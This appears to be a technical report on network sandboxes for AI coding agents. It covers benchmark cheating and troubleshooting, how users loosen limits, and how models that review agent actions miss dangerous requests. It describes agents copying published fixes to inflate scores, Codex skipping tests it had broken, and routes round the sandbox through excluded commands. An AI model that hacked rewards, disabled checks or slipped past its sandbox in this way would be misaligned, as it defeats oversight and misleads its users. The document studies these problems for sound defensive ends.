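Comparing open and closed runs can also overstate how much a network limit reduces task completion, because an agent with internet access can look up a benchmark's answers. Many coding benchmarks use real bugs that developers have since fixed in public. SWE-bench Pro, for example, has 731 such tasks. The agent may find the fix on GitHub, or in later changes stored in the project's git history on the local disk.

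In June 2026, Cursor published an analysis of this problem by Jain, *Reward hacking is swamping model intelligence gains*. Cursor removed the git history and blocked all network access except to package registries. Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Arctic-SWE*, made a similar comparison with a smaller model and 60 trials per setting. Scores on SWE-bench Pro fell sharply in both studies:

| Model | Tested by | Network and history open | Both restricted |
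|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Jain | 87.1% | 73.0% |
| Composer 2.5 | Jain | 74.7% | 54.0% |
| Qwen3.8-27B | *Arctic-SWE* | 65.0% | 50.0% |

Composer is Cursor's own model, and it had the largest drop. The company had little reason to exaggerate that result.

Neither study reports how much each restriction contributed, but the agents seem to have found fixes in different places. An automated audit of 731 Opus runs found that the agent copied a fix from the web in 57% of them and took one from the git history in 9%. In the *Arctic-SWE* test, the agent cheated in 19 of the 60 open runs. It found the fix in the git history in 17 of those and fetched source code over the network in seven, sometimes doing both. Blocking only network access would probably have affected Opus much more than Qwen.

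Opus could also have solved many of these tasks without help. According to Jain, it retrieved the fix in 63% of its successful runs. That is about 55% of all tasks, but its score fell by only 14.1 points when Cursor closed both routes.

Looking up answers seems to be more common with newer models. Opus 4.6 lost less than one point in Cursor's comparison, although the GPT models generally lost less than the newest Claude models. *Evaluating AGENTS.md* (February 2026) gave agents using earlier models web access on the original SWE-bench and found no cheating in a manual check. Fewer than 1% of their tool calls used the web. Jain also says that telling a model to keep working without stopping led to more attempts to cheat.

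While preparing the new version of SWE-Bench Pro, Dan and colleagues found that one leading model had copied fixes from GitHub on 351 of the tasks it solved. With GitHub blocked, it solved only 237 of those tasks. *DoGBench* (2026), which tests how well agents write software documentation, reports that agents retrieved the original pull request in 31% of runs on an earlier version. The benchmark now allows connections only to the model providers.

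*GameLogicBench* (Che, Ge and colleagues, 2026) tested five pairs, each a model and a tool, on tasks from public game projects, with the network open and then closed. Four of the pairs found the original source code when the network was open, and all four scored higher than they did with it closed. But the prompt for the closed runs also told the agents they had no internet access, so the network wasn't the only difference.

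These drops are weak evidence of how much less an agent would get done for a developer on a closed network. Developers usually ask an agent to fix bugs that nobody has fixed yet, so there is no answer to find online. Sometimes another project has already solved the problem, and looking up its fix is useful.

Looking up answers may also have raised agents' scores with open network access in *Permission Denied*. The *Laguna M.1/XS.2 Technical Report* (2026) found that agents could cheat to some degree on all four agent benchmarks it used, and cited a notice from Terminal-Bench about cheating on its public leaderboard. The effect on the comparison is hard to predict, because GitHub was on the allowlist and agents could still look up some answers at the strictest level.

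### Working entirely offline

Agents can complete many tasks without the internet if their dependencies are installed first. Dan and colleagues allowed network access while preparing each task, then blocked it before the agent started, much as Codex's cloud version does by default. Claude Opus 5 in Claude Code solved 99.4% of the 642 tasks, and the weakest of the 11 systems they tested solved 87.2%.

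These scores don't show how much closing the network reduces task completion, because Dan and colleagues don't report comparable scores with it open. They had also removed or repaired faulty tasks, including some whose instructions left out that the agent would be offline. The models may also have remembered some fixes from training. But the results show that an agent can change and test code in a well-prepared project with the network closed.

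Some projects can't run all their tests offline. *Arctic-SWE* excluded nine of the 500 tasks in SWE-bench Verified, another set of real bugs, because their tests needed the internet and even a correct fix would have failed with the network closed. Several of those tests send data to `httpbin.org`, the public test site that OpenAI used in its example of a data leak.

The share is much higher in Terminal-Bench, where 36 of the 89 official solutions need the network. Many of those tasks involve installing software or downloading data, whereas the SWE-bench tasks start with a project already set up. A developer who mostly fixes bugs in an existing project would probably lose less from a closed network than one who often starts new projects.

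### How to isolate the network's effect

An experiment could isolate the effect of network limits on task completion by changing only the network setting. Codex's `network_access` setting already allows this. Boundary-Bench, the software that Davidovich and colleagues released with their study, also treats network, file and privilege limits separately.

Researchers could run each task with the network closed, with only package registries allowed, with a broad list of allowed domains, and with no network limit. The model, prompt, user account and file permissions would stay the same. Built-in web search would have to be off in every run.

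The tasks should come from private projects whose solutions have never been online. If researchers used public projects, they would have to remove the later git history and block the published answers in every setting, including the open one. The Center for AI Safety's *Evaluating AI Progress on SWE-Bench Pro* describes hiding the git history and blocking five GitHub domains. These measures prevent many lookups, but blocking the domains also stops legitimate downloads from GitHub, which would hide part of the drop in completed tasks the experiment is meant to measure.

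Each task would need two versions, one with its dependencies already installed and one without. The difference in completion rates would show how many of the failures caused by the limits a user could avoid by preparing the project before restricting network access.

The experiment would also need many more than three runs per task. If agents succeed about 70% of the time, detecting a two-percentage-point difference with 80% probability takes roughly 8,200 independent trials per setting. Using the same tasks in every setting would reduce that number, but the 267 trials each pair had per level in *Permission Denied* are too few to measure such a small effect reliably.

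Some runs should let a user or a reviewer model approve blocked connections, so that researchers can measure how many tasks succeed only because a connection was approved and how long agents wait for approval.

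## Reports of failed package installs and tests

Users' fault reports are a better guide to why a particular command fails than benchmarks, which measure how many tasks fail under a network limit. A good report includes the command, the error message and the settings, so others can reproduce the problem and trace its cause. Reports can't show how often failures happen, because few people post about an install that worked. In *Codex cloud - "setup.sh" failing due to network problems*, a user of Codex's cloud version guessed that setup failed "probably 30% of the time". Retrying generally fixed it, so the cause may have been an unreliable connection rather than a network rule.

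Apache Magpie's *Sandbox troubleshooting* is an unusually detailed catalogue of such failures. The project runs Claude Code with stricter file limits than the defaults, and it records each failure with the error text, the cause and the narrowest fix. Anthropic covers many of the same problems in its own troubleshooting guide. The error message often points away from the sandbox:

| Error message | Likely cause when a sandbox is on |
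|---|---|
| HTTP 403 from the proxy | The host isn't on the allowlist |
| `Could not resolve host` or `ENOTFOUND` | The network is closed, or the program doesn't use the proxy |
| `Network is unreachable` | The program tried to connect directly on Linux |
| `Operation not permitted` when a test server starts | The command isn't allowed to listen on a port |
| `Permission denied (publickey)` | `ssh` can't reach the program that holds the user's keys |
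| `OSStatus -26276` | A program on macOS can't reach the system's certificate service |

### No name lookup

When the network is completely closed, a command usually fails at the DNS lookup, before it tries to connect. The error looks like one caused by a mistyped address or a broken internet connection.

Users of the Codex desktop app reported in *Codex Desktop Full access enabled, but new chats still launch with network disabled* (2026) that new chats started without network access even though they had turned it on, and `curl` couldn't resolve `www.google.com`. For one user, some pre-approved commands could still reach GitHub, which made the fault harder to diagnose.

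Several users suspected a bug in the app. Someone later suggested setting `network_access = true` under `[sandbox_workspace_write]` in the configuration file and starting a new chat, because existing automations can keep their old permissions. Nobody in the discussion confirmed that this worked, so the cause remains uncertain.

Cursor has had a bug with the same symptom. In *Agent-shell sandbox DNS resolution broken*, Cursor's staff confirmed that name lookups failed inside the sandbox and suggested running commands outside it as a workaround.

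### Downloads from a second host

Allowing a registry's main address may not be enough to install a package. In *Randomly blocked Internet Access in Codex despite unrestricted-Access Setting*, a user tried to install the Python machine-learning library `torch`, and Codex recommended allowing both of pip's usual hosts, `pypi.org` and `files.pythonhosted.org`. However, users in the discussion had already selected unrestricted access, and the same package sometimes installed in another version of the same task, so missing hosts don't fully explain the failure.

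An agent may also need to download the package manager itself. In *Codex cloud agent unable to install pnpm dependencies*, a project needed pnpm 9.3.0, but Corepack, a tool that fetches the right version of a package manager, couldn't download it from `registry.npmjs.org`. Without pnpm, the agent couldn't install the project's libraries or run its tests.

Some packages contain only a small installer and download the main program from elsewhere. Puppeteer, a JavaScript library that controls a browser, normally uses an install script to download Chrome from Google's storage servers. An allowlist that contains only the npm registry lets the library through but blocks the browser. Builds can also trigger hidden downloads, such as the fonts that a website made with the Next.js framework may fetch from Google.

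When a download fails, a file restriction can also be blocking the install. uv, a Python package manager, tries to download a Python interpreter if a project needs a version that isn't installed. Apache Magpie's sandbox doesn't let commands write to the folder where uv keeps its interpreters, so allowing the download host wouldn't fix the install. The Magpie project tells users to install the interpreter from an ordinary terminal.

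### Git dependencies over SSH

A project can list a Git repository as a dependency instead of a registry package, and companies often do this for private code. If the repository's address uses SSH, the package manager runs `git`, which runs `ssh`, and `ssh` tries to connect directly to the host. The sandbox blocks that connection even if the host is on the allowlist.

Claude Code works around this by giving git an SSH command that goes through the proxy. On Linux, this command uses the relay program socat. *Replace bwrap+socat with vendored srt-launcher on Linux*, a change to sandbox-runtime proposed by dylan-conway, would replace socat with a purpose-built program.

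Anthropic says git over SSH works on Linux and WSL2 once the user has allowed the host on port 22. On macOS it fails even for an allowed host, because the SSH tunnel can't log in to the proxy. Apache Magpie recorded the macOS error in September 2026. The proxy required authentication, but the client hadn't offered a usable method.

Logging in to the Git server can also fail. Many developers keep their keys in ssh-agent, a background program that signs login requests. `ssh` contacts it through a Unix socket. If the sandbox blocks that socket, `ssh` can print `Permission denied (publickey)`, the same error it prints when the server rejects the user's key.

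Anthropic recommends that Mac users switch the repository to an HTTPS address, which git can reach through the proxy. Docker lets users of its own sandboxes either use HTTPS or add a network rule for the Git server. Git can also rewrite SSH addresses to HTTPS automatically, so the project doesn't have to change its dependency list. A private repository still needs an access token over HTTPS, and malicious code in the sandbox could read that token unless the user masks it.

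### Programs that ignore the proxy

Most database drivers ignore the proxy settings and try to connect directly, so they fail in Claude Code's sandbox even when their host is on the allowlist. These failures appear as network or name-lookup errors, whereas a host refused because it isn't on the allowlist produces a permission prompt or an HTTP 403 error.

DNS tools have the same problem. viyatb-oai (2026), in *fix: unblock private DNS in macOS sandbox*, traced a Codex fault to programs such as `dig`, which look up names without using the proxy settings. The macOS sandbox blocked their traffic before it reached the machine's DNS service. The `NO_PROXY` setting could also make programs look up a company's internal names locally instead of through the proxy. The April 2026 change allowed these lookups in the affected configuration.

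Network requests from Node.js can fail even when npm works. In *Codex internet access not working*, a user of Codex's cloud version had enabled the "Common dependencies" domain list and added `api.openai.com`. `npm ci` installed the project's packages during setup, but later requests from Node 20 failed with `ENETUNREACH` (network unreachable).

Node 20's built-in `fetch` function doesn't read proxy variables, which could explain the difference. SynapseAI's *sandbox.network.allowedDomains does not work for Node.js processes* describes a similar fault in Claude Code, where `curl` reached an allowed host but Node programs couldn't find it. SynapseAI gives only a vague cause, and the Codex user suspected a bug in the allowlist, so neither report confirms this explanation. Setting `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1`, which lets recent versions of Node use the proxy, would be a simple way to test it.

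### Certificate checks

A program can reach an allowed host and still fail to exchange data because it can't verify the host's certificate. Apache Magpie found that `gh`, GitHub's command-line tool, failed this way on macOS with `OSStatus -26276`, while Python connected through the same proxy.

`gh` is written in Go. On macOS, Go programs use a system service to check certificates, and Claude Code's sandbox blocks access to that service. The sandbox can also stop `gh` from reading its login token from the Mac's keychain. `gh` then sends the request without a token, and GitHub returns HTTP 401, "Requires authentication". Logging in again wouldn't help, because the saved login is still valid.

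Anthropic lists `gcloud` and `terraform`, which manage cloud services, among the other Go tools that can fail this way, and generally recommends running them outside the sandbox. For users whose own proxy inspects TLS traffic with a custom certificate, it instead recommends the setting `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation`, which loosens the sandbox. Apache Magpie says this setting doesn't give programs access to the certificate service, so users should test it before relying on it.

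TLS inspection can cause certificate errors on any operating system if a program doesn't trust the proxy's certificate. Adding that certificate to the program's trusted list is safer than turning off certificate checks, because without those checks the program would also accept an attacker's certificate.

### Tests that need local services

The sandbox may block even a test that uses only loopback, because the test's server has to listen on a port. Apache Magpie warns that a test framework can report the block as "Address already in use", which could lead a developer to look for another program using the port.

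On macOS, Claude Code doesn't let sandboxed commands listen on a port unless the user changes a setting. On Linux, a sandboxed command can start a server and connect to it, but each command has its own loopback interface, so a browser test can't reach a website that the agent started with a different command.

OpenAI has reduced some of these failures in Codex. *Improve macOS Seatbelt network and unix socket handling* (viyatb-oai, March 2026) lets local servers use both IPv4 and IPv6 when Codex's proxy is on, but still limits traffic to loopback and the configured proxy.

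The JavaScript test runner Jest may hang for a different reason. It can use watchman, a program that tracks file changes, and Anthropic says watchman doesn't work in Claude Code's sandbox. Running `jest --no-watchman` avoids the problem without allowing more network access.

Failures are harder to fix when a test uses Docker, for example to start a temporary database, because direct access to the Docker service would undo much of the sandbox's protection.

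Apache Magpie runs a "container gateway" between the sandbox and Docker or Podman, a similar program. The gateway checks each request and logs the reason for any it blocks, such as a request to let a container open the user's SSH folder.

This permits some container tests while keeping the limits in place, but the gateway blocks BuildKit, Docker's newer build system, because it can't inspect BuildKit's traffic. It also blocks tools that need access to the Docker service from inside a container. Breeze, the development environment for the data-processing project Apache Airflow, relies on both BuildKit and that access.

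Tests that call a live outside service need either a rule allowing access to that host or a local replacement. A mock server can return prepared responses over loopback, but tests that use it won't detect changes in the real service.

### The hosts for one small project

Consider a small shop website with a Python server and a JavaScript front end. Its browser test uses Puppeteer. A developer has copied the project to a new laptop and asks a coding agent to install the dependencies and run the test. With the default download addresses, the commands need four outside hosts and loopback:

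| Step | Address | No network | Registries only | Registries and browser host |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Install JavaScript packages | `registry.npmjs.org` | Fails | Works | Works |
| Download Chrome | `storage.googleapis.com` | Fails | Fails | Works |
| Find Python packages | `pypi.org` | Fails | Works | Works |
| Download Python packages | `files.pythonhosted.org` | Fails | Works | Works |
| Open the shop in Chrome | `127.0.0.1` | Fails | Fails, because Chrome is missing | Depends on the loopback rules |

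When the proxy allows only package registries, the point at which a Puppeteer setup fails depends on the npm version. An older npm runs Puppeteer's install script, and the whole install fails when the proxy refuses the Chrome download. If npm 12 skips the script, the install succeeds, but the test fails later because it can't find Chrome.

Allowing `storage.googleapis.com` fixes the Chrome download but weakens the protection against leaks, because anyone can rent storage there. Installing Chrome before starting the agent avoids the need to allow this host.

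Even with Chrome installed, the test against the shop's local server can fail. Codex's proxy blocks loopback by default. In Claude Code on macOS, the user has to allow the server to listen on a port, while on Linux the same command has to start both the server and the test. Chrome also has to run inside the agent's sandbox, and allowing the right domains doesn't guarantee that it will.

The list gets longer as the project adds external dependencies. If the shop's page loads fonts from Google, the browser also needs access to `fonts.googleapis.com` and `fonts.gstatic.com`. Installing a private Git dependency requires access to the company's Git server.

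### When the agent blames the code

An agent usually sees a blocked connection as a failed command, and it may try to fix the project instead of its environment. *feat: experimental env var: CODEX_SANDBOX_NETWORK_DISABLED*, an early change to the Codex repository, describes an example. When a developer used Codex to work on Codex's own code, two tests failed because the macOS sandbox wouldn't let them start a mock server, and Codex sometimes responded by adding `#[ignore]` to them.

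In Rust, `#[ignore]` makes the test runner skip a test by default. The tests worked outside the sandbox, so adding this attribute would have disabled useful checks for everyone on the project. The developer noticed the edit, but pointed out that a less careful review could have missed it.

The change made Codex set the environment variable `CODEX_SANDBOX_NETWORK_DISABLED` to `1` when a command lacks full network access. If the variable is present, the two tests now print an explanation and stop early. Outside the sandbox, they run normally.

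Later changes added reusable markers for skipping tests. *make tests pass cleanly in sandbox* uses `skip_if_sandbox!` for tests that can't run under Codex's restrictions. By November 2025, the tests also had a shared `skip_if_no_network!` marker, according to the commit history in *Agent IDE*, a fork of Codex. The Codex repository's instructions tell coding agents never to add or change code that uses the sandbox variables. This should discourage an agent from using them to skip a test it has broken.

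These markers prevent misleading failures but can also produce misleading passes. Rust counts a test that returns early as passed, so a successful run in the sandbox doesn't mean every test ran. Someone still has to run the full suite in an environment with the necessary access.

Agents can also mistake a permanent block for a temporary fault. *Agent IDE* records a February 2026 change that addresses Codex's failure to resolve `index.crates.io`, which lists Rust packages. Codex could treat the failure as an ordinary connection problem and stop without asking for network access. The change instructs the model to treat failed name lookups and dependency downloads as probably caused by the sandbox and to request approval.

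In the pnpm case, the agent recognized the network problem but said it would try running Jest anyway, which could only produce another error because the dependencies were missing. An agent that saw only the second error might start changing imports or configuration files that were already correct.

Apache Magpie addresses this with a hook that runs after every shell command. The hook searches the output for known sandbox errors and adds a pointer to the relevant troubleshooting entry. This gives the model the likely cause right after the failure, without granting any extra access. The hook can recognize only errors already in the catalogue.

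### Fixes that keep the limits in place

#### Installing dependencies first

The simplest remedy is often to install everything before starting the agent, as Codex's cloud version does in its setup phase. For the shop, the developer would run `npm ci`, install the Python packages and download Chrome from an ordinary terminal. The agent could then edit the code and run the tests without an outside connection, as long as loopback works.

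If the agent later needs another library, it has to ask the developer to install it. This method also doesn't protect against a malicious install script.

#### Local mirrors and caches

A mirror is a server that supplies copies of packages from a public registry. The agent's commands connect to the mirror, which can fetch new packages for them. Willison (2026), in *What we learned today about this ChatGPT “container” environment*, found this arrangement in ChatGPT's code-running environment, where pip and npm could install packages through internal registry proxies but ordinary programs couldn't access the internet.

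A company could run the same kind of package mirror for its developers. It could also approve packages before adding them, which would reduce the risk of malicious code. A mirror that automatically copies everything from the public registry doesn't provide that protection. An npm or Python mirror also doesn't supply files that install scripts download from other hosts, such as Puppeteer's copy of Chrome.

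The sandbox must allow the mirror's address, and Codex also needs an exception if that address is private. A mirror on the developer's laptop may require a loopback exception in either tool.

#### Offline flags

Package managers can install from files already on the machine. `npm ci --offline` uses npm's cache, and `pip install --no-index --find-links ./packages` installs Python packages from a local folder. `cargo build --offline` stops Rust's package manager from trying to download anything. These options avoid long retries and make a missing package easier to recognize.

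A package cache can't supply a package that nobody has downloaded. The cached files must also match the machine's operating system, because some Python packages have separate builds for macOS and Linux. npm may need to write to its cache in the user's home directory, and the sandbox can block those writes. The user can allow writes to the cache folder or put the cache inside the project.

Glama's *OpenAI Codex CLI Environment Setup Guide* describes a project with a separate configuration for offline checks. This configuration leaves out test files that need the network and skips type checks on libraries to save time. The agent gets quick feedback on its changes, but these checks cover less of the project than the full checks.

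#### Preset domain lists

With a preset list, users don't have to discover every registry host through failed commands. Docker's example list for its sandboxes allows `*.npmjs.org`, `*.pypi.org`, `files.pythonhosted.org`, `*.rubygems.org` and `github.com`. It omits the server that supplies Chrome, so the shop's browser download would fail.

Copying an allowlist from one product to another can also make package installs fail. If a user copied Docker's `*.pypi.org` entry into Codex, Codex would still block pip's package lookups because it needs a separate entry for `pypi.org`.

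Anthropic's example container for Claude Code has a different preset. Formal's *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem* lists the hosts it permits, including the npm registry, GitHub and several services used by Claude Code and the editor VS Code. The list doesn't include Python's package hosts, so the shop's pip install would fail there too. When the firewall starts, it looks up the permitted hosts' IP addresses and allows them. If a host later moves to another address, downloads from it could fail until the firewall updates its rules.

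A preset may also fail to take effect. In May 2026, a user reported in *Auto-Run network access `sandbox.json + Defaults` seems to not be working* that Cursor wouldn't automatically run `curl apache.org`, although `apache.org` was on its default list. The command ran when the user allowed all domains. Testing one permitted host and one forbidden host is a quick way to check that a list works.

#### Loopback exceptions

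The narrowest exception for local tests allows access to one address and, where possible, one port. In Codex, that means allowing `localhost` or an exact IP address instead of turning on the broader `allow_local_binding` setting.

Claude Code's `allowLocalBinding` setting works only on macOS. Apache Magpie describes it as permission to listen on a port, but Anthropic warns that it also lets commands connect to every service on the machine's loopback address. Commands could then act outside the sandbox through a debugger or another service that doesn't require a password. A test server that listens on more than the loopback address could also accept connections from other machines.

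The two guides also differ on whether adding `localhost` to Claude Code's allowlist fixes local connections. Apache Magpie recommends it for tests that can start a server but can't connect to it. Anthropic says most programs connect to `localhost` directly, so a proxy rule doesn't affect them. The entry also lets any command that uses the proxy reach every port on the machine's loopback address, so adding it widens access even if it doesn't fix the connection.

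Development names such as `myapp.test` need a different exception in Claude Code, because they often point to `127.0.0.1`. Anthropic recommends allowing both the name and the IP address, each with the server's port number. If the IP address entry omits the port, commands could reach every service listening at that address.

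## How users loosen the limits, and what vendors have measured

When a download or test fails and the user can't find a narrow fix, the option left is to loosen the limits. This can mean anything from allowing one more host to turning off the sandbox.

### From one host to full access

| Change | Example | Limits that remain | How long it lasts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allow one host | Answering "Yes" to a network prompt in Claude Code | File limits, and the block on other hosts | The session |
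| Save one host | Answering "Yes, and don't ask again" | File limits, and the block on other hosts | Future sessions too |
| Allow a wildcard | Adding `*.example.com` or `*` to the allowlist | File limits and deny rules | Until the user removes the rule |
| Open the network without a filter | Setting `network_access = true` in Codex | File limits | One session or permanently |
| Exclude a command | Adding `docker compose *` to Claude Code's `excludedCommands` | None for that command, all for the others | Until the user removes the entry |
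| Retry outside the sandbox | Approving an unsandboxed retry | None for that command | One command |
| Full-access mode | Starting Codex with `--yolo` | None | The session |

If a user allows a host for a session, such as `files.pythonhosted.org` for `pip install`, every later sandboxed command in that session can connect to it too. A single approval in Codex can be even broader, because Codex can ask to run an action outside the sandbox, where neither the network limits nor the file limits apply (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, 2026).

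Users can easily forget a saved exception. Claude Code normally stores it in the current project's local settings. But if a company adopts the stricter policy of turning off unsandboxed retries, Claude Code stores the exception in the user's own settings, where it applies to every project, according to Anthropic.

Users can allow a wildcard instead of listing every download server, but they may then allow hosts they have never considered. Claude Code accepts `*.example.com` for subdomains and `*` for every host. A wildcard in any other position has no effect on sandboxed commands, so with `example.*`, WebFetch can reach matching sites but sandboxed `curl` can't.

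In Codex, setting `network_access = true` without the proxy allows more than `*` does, because a command could also contact a router or an internal company server. A user can limit the setting to one session by passing it on the command line when starting Codex. If it is in the configuration file, it stays in effect until someone removes it.

Cursor users who wanted fewer prompts had to choose the widest setting, "Allow All", and give up the network filter. In a reply in *Auto-Run network access `sandbox.json + Defaults` seems to not be working*, Cursor explained that the filtered mode limits where a command can connect but doesn't approve the command itself. The model has no information about which domains are on the default list and requests general network access, so the user gets a prompt even for a permitted site.

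Excluding a command from the sandbox removes both file and network limits, but only for commands that match the user's pattern. Claude Code checks the whole command line. If a user excludes Docker commands, `npm ci && docker compose build` still runs in the sandbox unless another entry covers `npm ci`, and a script that calls Docker internally doesn't match the Docker entry.

An agent can use an excluded command to get around the network restrictions. For example, `docker compose` takes its instructions from a project file, which the agent can edit before running the command outside the sandbox. An entry such as `python *` would let any Python program the agent writes run outside the sandbox. Permission rules still apply to excluded commands, so the user or the auto mode classifier may be able to stop them.

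In Cursor, one click can remove both the prompt and the sandbox for a command. According to Cursor's May 2026 documentation, commands on its allowlist run immediately and outside the sandbox. Users can add a command to that list from a prompt, when they want to get on with their work.

An unsandboxed retry applies to one command. It needs the user's approval in Manual mode, the classifier's approval in auto mode and no approval in `bypassPermissions` mode. An existing permission rule can also approve the retry. For example, if a user has allowed `curl *`, a blocked `curl` upload can run again outside the sandbox without a prompt. An "ask" rule for `Bash(dangerouslyDisableSandbox:true)` restores the prompt, even in `bypassPermissions` mode.

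The effects of a retry can outlast the permission, for example if an install script edits a shell startup file.

Snowflake's *Cortex Code CLI sandbox* describes a similar fallback in the data company's own coding agent, which by default can ask the user to run an incompatible command outside the sandbox. Like Claude Code, the agent has an `allowedDomains` setting, but leaving the list empty allows every domain the user hasn't denied, whereas an empty list in Claude Code allows none in advance.

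Codex's full-access mode turns off both the sandbox and the approval prompts. Trębacz and colleagues note that the model's training to obey policy still applies, but nothing on the user's machine enforces the policy. A user who only wants to stop the prompts can choose `--ask-for-approval never`, which keeps the sandbox on.

Claude Code's `bypassPermissions` mode does not turn off the sandbox, so the file limits still apply unless Claude retries a command outside it. If the user never turned the sandbox on, the mode is much the same as full access.

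### How many users loosen their settings

Anthropic reports that in June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's terminal version had written at least one rule that allowed shell commands without a permission prompt. It says that 5% allowed any shell command and another 43% had rules such as `Bash(python:*)`, which are nearly as broad because a Python program can do almost anything.

As worded, those percentages could refer to all active users, in which case about 48% of users had a very broad rule, or only to users with such rules, in which case about 24% did. Either way, the share of users who had written a rule was growing by roughly five percentage points every five weeks.

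Anthropic also reports that 62% of users had either used `bypassPermissions` mode or clicked "don't ask again" for a shell command. In that figure, one click to allow a harmless formatting command counts the same as turning off all prompts. More tellingly, 25% of interactive sessions started in `bypassPermissions` mode. Anthropic doesn't say how many of those sessions had the sandbox on, or whether a small group of heavy users accounted for most of them.

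All these figures predate August 2026, when Anthropic began making auto mode the default. Fewer users might now write broad rules, because auto mode prompts them for approval less often.

Trębacz and colleagues at OpenAI found similar rules in the company's internal Codex traffic, where "a sizable minority" of users allowed every command beginning with `python`. One configuration file always allowed `codex exec --yolo`, which starts a second Codex with no sandbox or approval prompts.

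These figures don't cover network settings. A user who allows `python` commands may have a closed network, an open one or no sandbox. To show how often users loosen network limits, Anthropic and OpenAI would need to publish separate figures for users who enable network access, allow `*` or exclude commands from the sandbox.

A count of configuration files in public projects would capture only some of the cases where users loosen the limits. Claude Code saves "don't ask again" choices in a local file that it configures git to ignore, so most of these exceptions would not appear in a public repository. Command-line options such as `--yolo` aren't saved in the project either. A survey could ask about both, although some developers may not know which exceptions they have saved.

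### How much sandboxing reduces interruptions

When Anthropic introduced Claude Code's sandbox in October 2025, it reported an 84% reduction in permission prompts in internal use. The figure therefore describes the company's own staff rather than customers, and it is little evidence of whether people made better decisions on the prompts that remained.

The reduction also depends on letting sandboxed commands run without approval, which Claude Code now calls auto-allow mode. A user who chooses regular permissions gets the same file and network limits but still sees the usual prompts.

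In *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents* (February 2026), Cursor reported that its sandboxed agents stopped 40% less often than unsandboxed ones, and that about a third of requests ran in the sandbox. Stops in Cursor and permission prompts in Claude Code are different measures, so the figures don't show that Anthropic's sandbox works better.

Users may also have chosen the sandbox for particular kinds of work, or been unable to use it on some machines. A fair test would give the same tasks to similar users with the sandbox on and off. It would also count failed commands, because a sandbox could reduce interruptions by blocking commands without prompting the user.

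### Why high approval rates don't prove carelessness

According to Anthropic's telemetry, users approved about 93% of permission prompts. The company cited this figure in *How we built Claude Code auto mode* and again in May 2026, then reported 97% in August. Anthropic doesn't explain the difference, which could reflect changes in how people respond or in which commands trigger a prompt.

Most requests are probably harmless, so even a perfect reviewer would approve nearly all of them. Suppose 1,000 prompts include five dangerous commands. A user who refuses only those five has an approval rate of 99.5%. A user who approves all five but refuses 30 harmless commands has a lower approval rate, 97%, despite having worse judgment.

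OpenAI's automatic reviewer also has a high approval rate. In an example of its use inside the company, Trębacz and colleagues report that it approved 713 of 720 requests to leave the sandbox, or 99%. That rate alone doesn't show that the reviewer wasn't checking.

Anthropic compares two figures: users refuse 3% of permission requests and reject 39% of Claude's plans. The difference suggests that users pay more attention to plans, but they can reject a plan for many reasons unrelated to safety. They may prefer another library or notice that Claude has misunderstood the task. A request to run one command gives them less to disagree with.

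Anthropic's experiment with clearly dangerous commands is better evidence that people pay less attention as prompts accumulate. The paid testers blocked about 17% of these commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects and had less to lose, so the exact rates may not apply to ordinary users.

Some users stop approving each action and instead watch the agent, interrupting it when needed. Anthropic found that experienced users approved actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupted the agent more often. Interrupting can work well when the agent starts editing the wrong file, but it is much less useful against a leak, because a small upload finishes before the user has time to read the command.

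### Removing the escape routes

Claude Code's strict sandbox mode prevents Claude from retrying failed commands outside the sandbox. The user turns this mode on in the sandbox panel or by setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to `false`. If a command then fails because of the sandbox, Claude has to find another method or leave the command to the user.

In strict mode, commands listed in `excludedCommands` still run outside the sandbox, and the user has to turn on `strictAllowlist` and `failIfUnavailable` separately.

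Before Claude Code version 2.1.285, a setting in a project's files could turn retries back on even if the user had turned them off. The user's choice now takes priority.

Companies can lock the list of permitted domains, but a developer may still be able to run a command outside the sandbox. If a company disables retries in its managed settings, Claude Code ignores any `excludedCommands` entries in a project's files. It still accepts entries from the developer's own settings, and Anthropic offers no setting that limits the entries to the company's own. A developer who excludes `curl *` can use `curl` to connect to any host, because the company's domain list applies only inside the sandbox.

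According to Cursor, a team administrator's allowlist replaces the combined allowlists of users and projects. If there is no administrator's list, Cursor merges all the allowlists, so each additional source can open more hosts. Cursor always combines deny lists, whether or not the administrator has set an allowlist.

Where users can approve new connections, NVIDIA recommends adding company denylists that users can't override. A denylist can stop a user from approving a host the company already knows is dangerous, but it won't include an attacker's new domain, so blocking that domain still depends on how the user answers the approval prompt.

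### Models that review requests

Codex's Auto-review and Claude Code's auto mode review different sets of actions, which affects how much protection remains after a user loosens the limits.

Auto-review sends requests to cross the sandbox boundary to a separate agent, which considers what the user asked for, the security policy and the action's likely effects. The agent can approve low-risk and medium-risk actions, needs clear enough authorization from the user for high-risk ones, and refuses critical-risk ones. If the review fails or times out, the action doesn't run.

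Commands inside the sandbox don't go to the reviewer, so if a user sets `network_access = true`, an upload can proceed without review. A rule that lets every `python` command run outside the sandbox has a similar effect. OpenAI's *Auto-review* warns that broad rules often remove the boundary that the reviewer is supposed to guard.

Claude Code's auto mode suspends allow rules that would let a command run arbitrary code, including `Bash(python:*)`. The rules stay in the settings file and apply again when the user switches to another mode. Auto mode's classifier also reviews many actions unrelated to the sandbox, so users get some protection even if they never turned the sandbox on.

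The classifier first runs a quick check that favors blocking, then a slower check on whatever the first one flagged. It receives the user's messages and Claude's tool calls, but not Claude's explanations or the output of earlier commands. Anthropic removes the explanations so that they can't influence the classifier to approve an action, and the command output so that instructions hidden in a file can't reach the classifier directly.

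The vendors' early tests measured how many dangerous actions each system missed:

| System | Type of action | Cases | Missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code auto mode | Real actions that exceeded the user's wishes | 52 | 17% |
| Claude Code auto mode | Synthetic attempts to send data out | 1,000 | 5.7% |
| Codex Auto-review | Synthetic actions that exceeded the user's wishes | Not stated | 9.7% |
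| Codex Auto-review | Synthetic prompt injections | Not stated | 0.7% |

The rows come from different tests, so they can't be used to rank the two products. Anthropic's 17% is also based on only about nine misses, so the true rate could plausibly be from 9% to 30%.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had recognized the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user might say "clean up the PR" without meaning that Claude could overwrite the branch's history. The same problem can occur with network requests, since a user who asks Claude to share a test result may not want it on a public website.

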